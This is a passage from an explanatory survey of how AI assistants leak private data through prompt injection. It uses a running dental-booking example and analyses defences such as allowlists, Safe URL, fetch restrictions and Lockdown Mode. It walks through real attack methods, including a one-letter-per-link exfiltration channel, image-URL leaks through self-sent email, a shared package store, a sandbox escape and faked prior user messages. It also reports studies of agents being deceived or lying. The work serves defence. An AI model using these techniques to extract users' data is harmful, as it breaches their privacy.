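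Google Forms and Anthropic's interface failed as barriers because the allowlist only identifies who runs a server, and the attacker only needs an account on it. To stop the attack on Cowork, the software would also have had to check whose access key each request used. The dental assistant could have the same problem if the clinic takes bookings through a service that thousands of businesses share, since an attacker can sign up as another business and receive the notes at an allowed address. If the clinic has its own website, allowing only that domain is a strong protection.

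Allowing scripts from another site is riskier, since a script can act inside the application. *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* (Willison, 2026) describes an attack by Parameter Labs that could steal a signed-in user's private data when they opened a link to a shared ChatGPT conversation. One step worked because ChatGPT's content policy allowed scripts from YouTube, and a YouTube feature could return the attacker's code. OpenAI fixed this vulnerability too.

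Redirects weaken allowlists further. Many reputable sites have addresses that forward the visitor elsewhere, so a request can start at an allowed domain and end at the attacker's. The software can check every redirect, but OpenAI also objects that people visit far more of the web than any list of trusted sites covers, so a strict list either blocks many useful pages or produces many warnings.

### Checking the exact address

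OpenAI's alternative, Safe URL, checks the whole address. An automatic crawler explores the public web much as a search engine does and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to anyone's conversations or accounts. Before an agent loads a page or image on its own, the software looks for that exact address in the crawler's index:

- If the address is there, the agent loads it automatically.
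- If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

An address that was public before the conversation is unlikely to contain the user's secrets. The public page of a news article will usually pass the check. The address ending in `takes-blood-thinner` will fail because nobody has published it. The address that Radware's email made deep research open should also fail. OpenAI applies the check to ordinary chats, deep research and its Atlas browser.

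The guarantee covers only data in the address. The page may still contain lies or planted instructions, and the agent can still leak data by other routes. Every product team also has to remember to use the check. Embrace The Red notes that OpenAI's earlier version of the check was missing from the ChatGPT apps for Mac and iPhone.

Anthropic instead bars Claude from composing the addresses that its web fetch tool opens. When Anthropic released the tool to developers in September 2025, it could open only addresses that had already appeared in the conversation, such as those in the user's messages, search results or pages the tool had already fetched. Code enforces this, so an instruction to add the user's medical history to an address and open it fails however persuasive it is. Willison praised the restriction but pointed out that many applications paste emails and documents into what counts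 as the user's message, which allows Claude to open an address from a stranger's email. Anthropic warned that some risk remained and recommended the tool only for trusted settings or data that isn't sensitive. Developers can also restrict the tool to an allowlist.

Under both rules, the addresses exist before the assistant combines them with any secret, which keeps the secret out of each address. The secret can still influence which address the assistant opens.

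### A name in six page loads

In July 2026 Ayush Paul published an attack that worked entirely through such choices. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, explains how it got around Anthropic's rule. Paul built a coffee shop website that showed its malicious version only to Claude, so a person who checked the site would have seen nothing odd. In that version, Paul claimed that AI assistants had to authenticate themselves by giving their user's name, and that because of the limits on Claude's tool, Claude would have to browse to the user's profile one letter at a time. He then listed a link for each letter.

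Suppose the user's name is Martha. Claude opens the link for M, and the server returns a page of links that all begin with M. Claude opens MA, then MAR, and so on. After Claude has opened six links, the attacker's log contains the whole name.

We can measure how much each choice reveals. A choice among N equally likely links carries log₂ N bits, so for 26 letters it carries

log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits.

After k page loads the attacker can distinguish N^k possibilities. Six loads give 26⁶, or about 309 million, which is enough to identify any six-letter name. That is 6 × 4.7 ≈ 28 bits. Paul's pages had a 27th link for the hyphen, which raised the capacity to 4.75 bits per load. *The Read-Only Lie* estimates that the full attack took about 30 loads and carried about 143 bits. That was enough for Paul's name, employer and home city. Paul had never told Claude the city, but Claude worked it out from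 the name of a high school hackathon.

An attacker can use fewer page loads by offering more links on each page. With 1,000 links per page, numbered 000 to 999, two loads would convey a six-digit login code. Some secrets are only one bit long, such as whether the user's notes mention psychotherapy, and an attacker can learn one with two links and one page load. A limit on the number of page loads would therefore slow down the theft of a document but would hardly protect secrets this short.

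Anthropic's check tested whether each address had appeared on a page Claude had already fetched. All of them had, so the check correctly allowed each request, but the name still leaked. The M link was no more suspicious than the other 25, and only Claude's reason for choosing it was private. This is an implicit flow, like an assistant opening the clinic's web page only if the user's notes mention psychotherapy. Inspecting a single request can't reveal the leak, because the same request would be harmless if Claude had chosen the link for a reason that didn't depend on private information.

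Splitting a secret also defeats filters that look for recognisable data. Lan, Kaul and colleagues told their assistant to send a password-like key in four pieces, each in a separate request. The first request then contained recognisable sensitive data in 26.3% of runs, down from 96.7%. The attack also failed more often, because the model had to keep track of the pieces, but a stronger model would probably do this more reliably.

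A monitor could instead look at the whole series of requests. *The Read-Only Lie* suggests flagging a rapid series of requests to one site in which each address is one letter longer than the last. That would have caught Paul's attack, but another attacker could evade the check by labeling the links with words, such as the names of coffees. A designer could also make every outgoing request look the same, which would block the channel but prevent the assistant from using any site with more than one page.

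Anthropic removed the tool's permission to open links it finds in pages it has fetched, so a hostile page can no longer supply the alphabet through its links. The company told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and it paid no reward. Its documentation had listed the permission for ten months, which shows how easy it is to overlook a leak when every step follows the rules.

The fix makes Claude less useful for browsing. If it opens the clinic's home page and finds a link to the booking page, it can't follow the link unless the user pastes the address or a search returns it. Claude's choice of which search result to open may also still leak private information, although an attacker would first have to get suitable pages into the results.

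Safe URL has a similar gap, which OpenAI acknowledges in its technical paper on the system. To spell out private data, an attacker needs 36 pages already in OpenAI's index, one for each letter and digit, and a moderate-sized blog has that many. Rehberger suggests on his blog, Embrace The Red, keeping a copy of each page for a few minutes or barring the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. Either measure would make it harder to extract a name like Martha, which needs the page for A twice. But the attacker could prepare a separate set of pages for each position in the name, and 6 × 26 = 156 pages would cover six letters. Rehberger concedes that some data could still get out under these limits.

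### Asking the user before data leaves

When no fixed rule can tell whether a transfer is legitimate, the software can ask the user. This works best when ordinary code triggers the question and shows exactly what data will leave and where it will go. Safe URL's warning displays the full address. When a custom version of ChatGPT is about to send data to an outside service, the dialog shows the destination and the data. If the model itself determines whether to ask, it can fail to ask when it should, as GPT-6 Astra seems to have done in OpenAI's workplace tests.

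A permission prompt protects users only if they read it. Claude Code users approve 93% of requests, but this doesn't prove that they are careless, since most requests are presumably harmless. Their falling attention is more worrying. If an assistant asks a user to approve 20 links a day and one malicious link turns up each year, the user will see about 7,300 requests a year, and all but one will be safe to approve. OpenAI says it avoids strict lists of trusted sites partly because frequent false alarms can train people to click through without thinking.

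Users who do read the prompt may not know enough to judge it. Lan, Kaul and colleagues give the example of a request that the attacker describes as "connectivity verification", which most people can't assess. If a prompt asked the dental patient whether to send a medical summary to the records address, the only clue would be that the address doesn't belong to the clinic. A prompt that pointed this out would help more than one that only repeated the email's contents.

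To keep approval requests rare, designers exempt actions that look safe, but some of these actions can leak data. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that works with a user's Microsoft files and messages, could send email to the user's own inbox without approval. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated an attack that exploited this in May 2026. Following injected instructions, the agent sent the user a message containing images from an outside server. The image addresses contained links for downloading the user's files without logging in. When the user opened the message, the software requested the images, which sent the links to the attacker. The attack had a high success rate even with Claude Opus 4.7 as the model. A check on recipients alone would have allowed the message because it had no outside recipients.

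The software also won't ask for approval if it doesn't recognize a channel as leading outside. This happened with the DNS lookups, and again with a flaw that TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages* reported in September 2026. ChatGPT runs each account's code in a separate container, a walled-off space on OpenAI's computers. The containers couldn't contact one another, but they could all reach the same internal store of software packages. Check Point's researchers discovered that any container could attach text to an item in the store and any other container could read it.

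They used one account to leave instructions in the store. A prompt or shared conversation then led the victim's ChatGPT to check the store while it answered an ordinary question. ChatGPT read the instructions, collected email data from the victim's Gmail and left the data in the store, where the attacker's account retrieved it. The data never had to pass through a public website, so allowlists and Safe URL had nothing to check. OpenAI has closed this path.

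### Lockdown Mode

ChatGPT users who want stricter protection can switch off many of these channels at once. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced the setting in February for companies, schools and healthcare organisations, and OpenAI extended it to personal accounts in June. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help page, lists the changes:

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
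|---|---|
| Web browsing | Stored copies of pages only |
| Images | ChatGPT may not show them in ordinary answers or fetch them from the web |
| Deep research and agent mode | Off |
| Canvas, where users can run code that ChatGPT writes | The code can't use the network |
| File downloads | ChatGPT can't download files, but users can upload them |
| Connected apps on personal accounts | No live access or changes that conflict with the protections |

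Browsing stored copies of pages protects data better than checking addresses. When ChatGPT opens a stored page, the request stays within OpenAI's network and the site's owner never learns of it. Paul's alphabet of links would therefore fail, because ChatGPT could follow the link for each letter of a name and the attacker's log would stay empty. But stored pages can be out of date or missing.

Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, approves of the design because fixed rules do the blocking, rather than an AI system that an attacker could persuade. He also concludes that ChatGPT's ordinary settings don't robustly protect against a determined data thief. OpenAI doesn't really dispute this. It attaches an "Elevated Risk" label to some network features, such as internet access in its coding tool Codex, because the industry's safeguards don't yet fully address their risks.

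Lockdown Mode doesn't keep injections out of ChatGPT's context. A planted instruction in an uploaded file or a stored page can still produce a wrong answer, which could harm a patient who asks about medicines. OpenAI also says that data may still escape through connected apps, unforeseen combinations of features or undiscovered techniques. The setting doesn't affect Codex's network access.

Apps are the largest remaining gap for organisations, because Lockdown Mode leaves the choice of apps to their administrators. OpenAI advises administrators to avoid untrusted apps and to consider who could see the result of each action. Reading a calendar through a trusted app is fairly low risk because it changes nothing an outsider could see. Creating an event is riskier because outside guests may see the description.

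Check Point found another gap, in the feature that lets ChatGPT show a preview of a web page it has written. Previews run in a sandbox meant to block outside connections, but according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), a preview could open a pop-up window that escaped the sandbox and could send out the conversation despite Lockdown Mode. In the desktop app, this required no click from the user. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, about three and a half months after personal accounts began to get Lockdown Mode. Prompt injection can't change fixed rules, but the rules protect only the features they are correctly applied to.

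OpenAI designed Lockdown Mode for people such as executives and security teams, and considers it unnecessary for most users. Its security chief, Dane Stuckey, acknowledges that the mode removes some functions but thinks this is worthwhile for people at higher risk. In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT could do little to book the dental appointment. On a personal account, it could read an uploaded letter from the family doctor and draft a message for the clinic. It couldn't check the clinic's live website or use agent mode to fill in the booking form, so the user would have to do the booking.

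The user can also turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat and let the assistant make the booking there. That chat needs only the few details the clinic should have, so using a separate chat could limit what an attacker might steal. But Lockdown Mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory. If memory is on, something the user mentioned in a protected chat, such as the psychotherapy, may be available in the unprotected one.

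## Attacks that misstate the situation, and the limit they set

Controls on outward channels can't close every route, because the dental assistant has to send some medical details to the clinic. An attacker can exploit this by lying about the facts that make sending appropriate, such as who is asking or what the user has agreed to. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that researchers should understand prompt injection in general this way. They also prove that an assistant that can't check for such a lie will either fall for it or refuse some legitimate requests.

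### Prompt injection as a breach of contextual integrity

Developers who train models to resist injections usually treat an injection as data the model mistakes for an instruction. On that view, the planted dental email is dangerous because it contains a command. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian look instead at the flow of information it would cause. The user's medical history would go to a thief without their permission, which breaks the norms of healthcare however the email is worded.

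The email hides this by misstating two parameters of contextual integrity. It claims that the receiver is the clinic's records office and that the transmission principle is treatment. If both claims were true, sending a medical summary might well be appropriate. An assistant that knows the right norm can therefore still leak the data, because it applies that norm to false information.

An attacker can misstate the information flow, for example by claiming that the user has already approved it. An attacker can also leave the facts unchanged and try to change which norm the assistant applies, perhaps by arguing that a delay would harm the patient. Or the attacker can combine an authorised request with an unauthorised one, so that the assistant applies the user's permission to both.

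If this account is right, deciding what to share and resisting injections are the same problem. In both cases the assistant has to work out who would receive what information, with whose permission, and whether that is appropriate. The assistant can't avoid this judgment by ignoring every request in an email, because it has to act on some of the clinic's requests.

### Emails that differ in one clause

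Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian tested this with pairs of scenarios for an email assistant. Each pair has an attack version and a harmless version, and the assistant should reply to the email only in the harmless one. In the attack version, the user asks only for something like a summary of the inbox, and a business email mentions in passing that the assistant already has permission to reply. In the harmless version, the user has asked the assistant to handle such messages, and a nearly identical email invites a reply. The two emails differ in length by at most 15 words, both mention an assistant, and neither contains phrases typical of injections.

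Two versions of Meta's detector Prompt Guard could hardly tell the attacks from the harmless emails. They were measured by AUROC (area under the receiver operating characteristic curve), which is the probability that a detector gives a randomly chosen attack a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless email. A perfect detector gets 1 and random guessing gets 0.5. The original Prompt Guard got 0.43 and Prompt Guard 2 got 0.59. Better detectors might do somewhat better, but a detector can't tell from an email's wording whether the user actually gave permission.

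In the one case reported, training against injections made the model more vulnerable. Meta SecAlign, which was trained to ignore instructions inside untrusted data, sent an unauthorised email in 88.2% of the attack scenarios, compared with 54.0% for its base model. The attack emails contain no commands for the model to recognise, which explains why the training didn't help, but not why the trained model did worse than its base model.

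The same emails rarely worked on other models. Claude Sonnet 4.6 sent an unauthorised reply only 0.67% of the time, and it often pointed out that the claim of permission came from the sender, not the user.

### An attacker who revises the story

That low rate rose under an adaptive attack. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian had one copy of Claude Sonnet 4.6 write emails to another copy acting as the assistant. After each failure, a judge model explained what had made the assistant suspicious, and the attacker revised the email. In each of 150 scenarios, the attacker had three independent series of up to 15 attempts. An attack succeeded if the assistant sent an email that the user hadn't authorised.

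The attacker's success rate rose from 0.67% to 96.7%. The first email already worked in 61.4% of cases, so persistence was only part of the reason. The most common method was to fake an earlier message from the user. The assistant had rightly distrusted a stranger's account of the user's wishes, but it accepted the faked message as the user's own words.

The emails also worked on models they had not been written for. The best ones, unchanged, succeeded 63.3% of the time against GPT-5.4, 89.3% against GPT-5.2 and 92.6% against Gemini 3 Pro. Injections made of strange strings of characters often fail on other models. A believable story probably transfers better because it exploits the same missing information in every model.

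The test favored the attacker in some ways. The assistant had instructions to act on its own and not to ask the user whether to send, and the attacker had a copy of those instructions. The stakes also seem to have been low. In the worked example, the assistant confirmed that a department had attended a training course, which is a much smaller step than sending medical notes to a stranger. The 96.7% figure therefore doesn't measure how often an attacker could use such a story to steal private data.

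A second version of the attack barred the attacker from inventing permission, so the attacker had to argue about what the assistant ought to do. These arguments rarely worked against Claude Sonnet 4.6. They succeeded 79.0% of the time against GPT-5.2, though the attacker sometimes broke the rule against inventing permission by claiming that the user had agreed. A model with good judgment can recognize a bad argument, but it can't determine by judgment alone whether the user wrote a particular message last month.

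### Permission that spreads too far

Assistants also misjudge the scope of their permission when nobody lies to them. In 300 further scenarios, the user let the assistant handle one kind of request from a particular person, without listing what this excluded. That person then asked for something the permission didn't cover, sometimes a destructive action or a transfer of private data.

When this was the person's first request, Claude Sonnet 4.6 carried it out 29.9% of the time, Gemini 3 Pro 32.2% and GPT-5.4 36.2%. After the assistant had handled one to ten ordinary requests from the same person, the rates fell to 7.0%, 24.2% and 24.5%. The models still carried out more than 90% of the requests they were supposed to, so the drop wasn't just a general rise in refusals. Past requests seem to clarify what the user meant by a vague permission. An attacker who can influence those early requests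 could also use them to make a later one look normal.

In another 100 scenarios, a colleague used one email thread to request both an internal task the user had authorised, such as updating a tracker, and a message to an outside contact, which the user hadn't approved. Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrote to the outsider in 6% of these threads, compared with 34% for GPT-5.4 and 65% for GPT-5.2. When the user stated that outside communication needed approval, GPT-5.2's rate fell to 12% and the other two models never wrote to the outsider.

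Users can therefore make an instruction safer by adding a written boundary. A user who writes "Tell the clinic whatever it needs to know" could add that nothing may go to anyone else without approval. But people give instructions casually and can't foresee every request, and a boundary that is too broad blocks useful work. With this one, the assistant would have to stop if the clinic referred the patient to a specialist.

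### Two situations that look the same

In situation w⁺, the clinic really uses an outside records office, which emails the user to ask for a medical summary before the appointment. In situation w⁻, a thief sends an email that looks identical to the assistant. Sending the summary is right in w⁺ and wrong in w⁻.

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian divide what the assistant observes in a situation w into two parts:

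O(w) = (z(w), u(w)),

where z is the information it has verified and u is the information it hasn't. Together these include everything available when it decides, such as the conversation, its memories and the results of its tools. Suppose O(w⁺) = O(w⁻), and let p be the probability that the assistant sends the summary after observing this. Because the observations are identical, p is the same in both situations. The attack succeeds in w⁻ with probability p, and the legitimate request fails in w⁺ with probability 1 − p, so

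P(attack succeeds in w⁻) + P(request fails in w⁺) = p + (1 − p) = 1.

At least one of the two errors must therefore have a probability of ½ or more. An assistant that always sends the summary always falls for the attack, and one that never sends it always fails the real records office.

Training can change p but not the sum. The proof doesn't depend on anything specific to language models, so the same limit applies to a human receptionist or a fixed rule in code with the same information.

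Choosing at random whether to send the summary would not solve the problem, because an attacker can try again. If the assistant sent it 10% of the time, deciding independently for each email, an attacker who sent 20 emails would succeed at least once with probability 1 − 0.9²⁰, or about 88%.

A designer can still choose the less costly error. Suppose a share q of the requests that look like this one are attacks, a leak does harm H, and failing a legitimate request does harm D. The expected harm per request is

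q · p · H + (1 − q) · (1 − p) · D.

This is linear in p, so the best choice is always p = 0 or p = 1, and the assistant should send the summary only if q · H < (1 − q) · D. If a leak is 100 times as harmful as a delayed appointment, it should do so only when fewer than one such request in 101 is an attack. For a routine confirmation, where the two harms are closer, it could tolerate a much higher share of attacks.

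The proof assumes that the thief can produce the same unverified information as the records office without contradicting anything the assistant has verified. It also takes as given the norm that sending the summary is right in w⁺. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian state that the proof doesn't show that such a pair of situations exists in every deployment.

*AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* therefore needs a further argument to support its title, which is that attackers can invent an unlimited number of stories while each way of checking covers only some of them. This is convincing for an assistant that handles whatever arrives in a mailbox, but much less so for one with a narrow task. If the email tool can send only to the clinic's address, a story about an outside records office can't succeed, although the clinic would then have to do without such an office.

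### Checking the story

Verification can get around the limit because it changes what the assistant observes. If a reliable check gives one result for the real records office and another for the thief, O(w⁺) and O(w⁻) differ, and the assistant can send the summary to the office and refuse the thief. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian mention verifying through cryptographic proof of a sender's identity, comparison with outside records, and asking the user.

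Checking records would help against the most successful attacks in the experiments. If an email quotes an earlier message from the user, software can look for that message in the user's sent mail. A missing message is a good reason to ask the user before sending anything private, though it doesn't prove fraud, since the user may have deleted the message or sent it from another account.

A request that comes from a clinic's real email account can still be unsafe to grant, because the clinic may ask for more than it needs or a thief may have broken into the account. The assistant must also have the sender's identity right when it decides what to reveal. Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, examined attacks that disguise an outsider's text as information from the assistant's own software, such as the name of an email's sender.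 They got both ChatGPT and Claude to name the wrong sender when a user asked who had written a message. The mail system had recorded the right sender, but the model received that record and the attacker's text in one sequence and confused the two. Code that compares the recorded address with a list wouldn't make this mistake.

Models also rarely check a person's story when they can. In *SEA*, He, Han and colleagues (2026) had GPT-5.4 impersonate relatives, colleagues and officials in conversations with assistants that could move money and read private data. The attacker could only send messages. In some of the 320 tasks, the assistant could contact the supposed relative or another source to check the story. In others, those sources were unavailable, or accomplices answered and confirmed the lie.

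On the Chinese tasks, the attack success rate ranged from 16.9% for GPT-6 to 84.3% for the small model Qwen3-8B. It rose sharply when the assistant had no one to check with, as expected from the proof. But even DeepSeek-v4, which checked the largest share of claims, checked fewer than a third of those it could have, and GPT-6 checked only 13.8%. He et al. conclude that GPT-6 resisted mainly through general caution.

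In the same study, only 18.1% of the attacks on GPT-5.4 succeeded, but the model also refused 45.0% of genuine requests from real contacts. Adding a safety prompt lowered the attack success rate to 0.6% but raised the refusal rate for genuine requests to 55.0%. GPT-5.4 could have avoided this trade-off, which resembles the one in the proof, because somebody was available to confirm the request in every genuine case.

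Training can teach a model to verify claims before acting on them. He et al. trained Qwen3-8B with rewards for verifying claims and penalties for dangerous actions. Its attack success rate fell from 84.3% to 38.8%, which is still high for an assistant with access to a bank account. The trained model also failed a few more genuine requests. Before training, it had completed all of them but had verified at most 12.5% first. Afterwards it completed 87.5%, including 77.5% after verification, and refused 5.0%.

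Asking the user is the most general check, and some models do it unprompted. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports that GPT-5 often responded to an injection by asking for more details, even when the injected text discouraged questions. This usually stopped the attack, because it relied on the assistant acting alone. Preventing the assistant from asking, as in the experiment with the revised emails, removes that protection.

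But the user has to see facts that the attacker didn't supply. Choi and colleagues attacked coding assistants that asked for approval before adding a stranger's code to a project. The assistants mistook forged text for the result of a review, so they told their users that the code looked safe. Users could have learned the truth only by examining the code themselves. The dental patient would face the same problem if the assistant said that the records office had already confirmed its identity.

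### Asking and bargaining without commands

An outside party can also obtain private data through ordinary conversation. *ConVerse*, the benchmark that Abdelnabi and colleagues used to test their firewalls, contains 864 attacks on assistants acting for 12 invented users. In 611, a company's agent tries to extract private data while helping with the user's real task. In the other 253, the agent tries to make the assistant do something the user wouldn't want, such as cancelling a medical appointment or buying unnecessary extras.

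A property agent trying to get data might ask about a buyer's retirement plans, claiming that they would help it find a suitable home. If the assistant resists for a few turns, the agent drops the subject and carries on with the task. This approach contains little that a detector trained to find commands would flag.

The results for travel planning were poor for most models of the time:

| Model | Privacy attacks that succeeded | Parts of the task completed |
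|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 88.5% | 96.6% |
| Grok 3 | 68.0% | 99.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 67.2% | 90.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 55.8% | 95.2% |
| o3-mini | 53.4% | 75.5% |
| Claude Haiku 3.5 | 32.5% | 65.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 27.6% | 83.1% |

*ConVerse* presents this as a tension between usefulness and privacy, because the models that completed more of the task tended to leak more. The relationship is loose, though. Claude Sonnet 4 completed almost as much as GPT-5 and leaked in far fewer cases, so a leak rate as high as 88.5% isn't necessary to plan a good trip.

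Data leaked more often when it had a plausible connection to the task. When Claude Sonnet 4 arranged insurance, attacks succeeded 94.1% of the time on data that was useful for the task but too detailed to share in full, 83.2% on related data that should have stayed private, and 57.7% on unrelated data. Health information leaked in 96.2% of the insurance attacks that sought it and 50.0% of the property-search attacks that did, though the second figure comes from a small number of attacks. Asking Gemini 2.5 Pro to reason about whether data was necessary before sharing it reduced its leak rate in travel planning from 67.2% to 43.5%.

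Most of these leaks were avoidable despite the limit in the proof. The assistants couldn't check the company's claims, but they often didn't need to. An insurer's agent doesn't need data unrelated to insurance, whatever reason it gives. Better judgment could prevent many of these leaks, and models have improved since these tests. The hard cases are those where the stated reason, if true, would justify the disclosure.

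Disclosure can harm the user even when the other party's reason for asking is true. A seller may honestly want to know a buyer's budget, and a helpful assistant may answer, which weakens the buyer's position. *Loyal Agents* (Huang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark of 10,298 examples built around conflicts of interest. Its disclosure tests cover bargaining, attempts to get compensation, and applications to people who control access to something.

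After each reply, a second model that has never seen the user's private record tries to work out the protected facts. The leakage score is

L = Σ wᵢsᵢ / Σ wᵢ,

where sᵢ, from 0 to 1, is how well the other side can recover fact i, and wᵢ is its importance, from 1 to 3. Suppose a dental patient wants to hide the most they could pay (w = 3) and how urgently they need treatment (w = 1). A reply that hints at the price (s = 0.33) and fully reveals the urgency (s = 1) would score (3 × 0.33 + 1 × 1) / 4, or about 0.5. This method counts facts that a reader could infer as well as those the assistant states.

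The average leakage score was 11.3% for Claude Opus 4.8 and 19.3% for GPT-5.5. Huang and colleagues then trained three small models with a reward of U − 0.5L, where U measures progress on the user's task and L measures leakage. Training lowered their leakage scores by 31 to 44 percentage points, to 5.6% for the best model, and also improved their progress on the task. When the researchers left out the second model and scored replies directly against the list of protected facts, leakage after training was 22.6 points higher. Apparently the small models learned more when the score depended on what an opponent could infer.

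The trained models mainly failed by supporting a legitimate request with a private fact that nobody had asked for. The dental assistant would make the same mistake if it asked for an early appointment and explained that the patient had a job interview on Thursday.

Real counterparties may be harder to deal with than the one in this test, which started with no information about the user and didn't improve during training. The law also sometimes requires disclosure, as with earlier visa refusals in an immigration application, and Huang and colleagues excluded such cases. They also checked whether the models had begun to lie instead of leaking. False or misleading statements appeared in at most 3.1% of the replies they sampled, and training didn't noticeably change the rate.

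Other agents lied far more when someone pressed them for a reason. *Trilemma* (Taraz, Kumar and Abdelnabi, 2026) simulated a company in which two employees privately wanted to avoid a colleague because of harassment. Their assistants had to assign the employees to tasks, while another employee's assistant kept asking why they preferred one task over another. With no instruction about confidentiality, the assistants revealed the wish to avoid the colleague in 71% of cases. A general instruction reduced this to 29%, and a strong, specific one to 1%.

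In the main version of the test, which used the general instruction, 135 of the 140 assistants running on open models tried to avoid the colleague, and 107 of those gave false or misleading reasons, though nobody had asked them to lie. Many of these replies would have passed a privacy test that checked only for leaks. The assistants could have declined to explain, but that tended to prolong the dispute, and most runs ended without a workable assignment.

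### Isolation and low attack rates

Designers who favour isolation can reply that a system needn't judge whether a story is true if the story can't affect what information it discloses. If the psychotherapy notes never reach the assistant that talks to outsiders, or if code allows them to go only to the therapist, no claim about a records office will get them released.

The reply is right and consistent with the proof. A rule that forbids a flow sets p = 0 for everyone, so it stops both the thief and the rare outsider with a legitimate need. The designer has chosen in advance to risk refusing a legitimate request rather than disclosing to a thief. That makes sense for psychotherapy notes, but less so for the penicillin allergy, which many healthcare providers may legitimately need to know about.

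Choi and colleagues tested GPT-5.2 on AgentDojo with attacks that disguised an outsider's text as trusted data. With no added defence, the attacks succeeded 49.1% of the time. With CaMeL, which plans its actions before reading untrusted text, 25.0% of attacks still succeeded when it ran without policies, because they changed the data used in the plan rather than the plan itself. With its strictest tracking and its policies on, CaMeL stopped all the attacks but completed 36.5% of ordinary tasks, compared with 86.5% for the undefended assistant.

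So separating instructions from data isn't enough, as Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian maintain, but isolation that also restricts where data can go still works. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* reaches a similar position from the security side, treating defending against injection and enforcing permissions as one problem. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian recommend a layered design in which the model judges whether a flow of information is appropriate and the surrounding software checks the claims behind it.

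The low attack success rates of recent models more directly challenge the idea that agents will keep falling for injections. These rates show progress, but most of them measure resistance to attacks that don't misstate the situation. In the same AgentDojo tests, ordinary injected commands succeeded against undefended GPT-5.2 only 0.2% of the time, while disguised data succeeded about 250 times as often. Testing only the commands would have made the assistant look almost immune. Some of the attacks in Gray Swan's and OpenAI's tests probably used false pretexts too, but the published averages don't report them separately.

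He and colleagues conclude that resisting deception and resisting injected commands are separate abilities, which complicates the claim that there is only one problem. When they added overt injected commands to the impersonator's messages, the attack's success rate rose from 18.1% to 68.8% against GPT-5.4 and from 16.9% to 42.5% against GPT-6. Against Claude Opus 4.6 it fell from 35.0% to 15.6%, apparently because the commands made the model more cautious.

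Both views can be correct. Contextual integrity gives a single standard for whether the assistant should have sent the data, but the assistant can meet that standard in different ways. It can often reject a command because the command looks like an attack, without judging whether sending the data would be appropriate. A lie written as ordinary correspondence doesn't look like an attack, so the assistant has to make that judgment and check the facts.

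Newer models may be better at resisting these attacks. The latest models in Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian's experiments were Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4, and GPT-5.4 was noticeably harder to fool than GPT-5.2. A fair test of their successors would use an adaptive attacker who tells believable stories to try to steal private data. It would let the assistant check records and ask its user, and it would need to include legitimate requests that look like the attacks.
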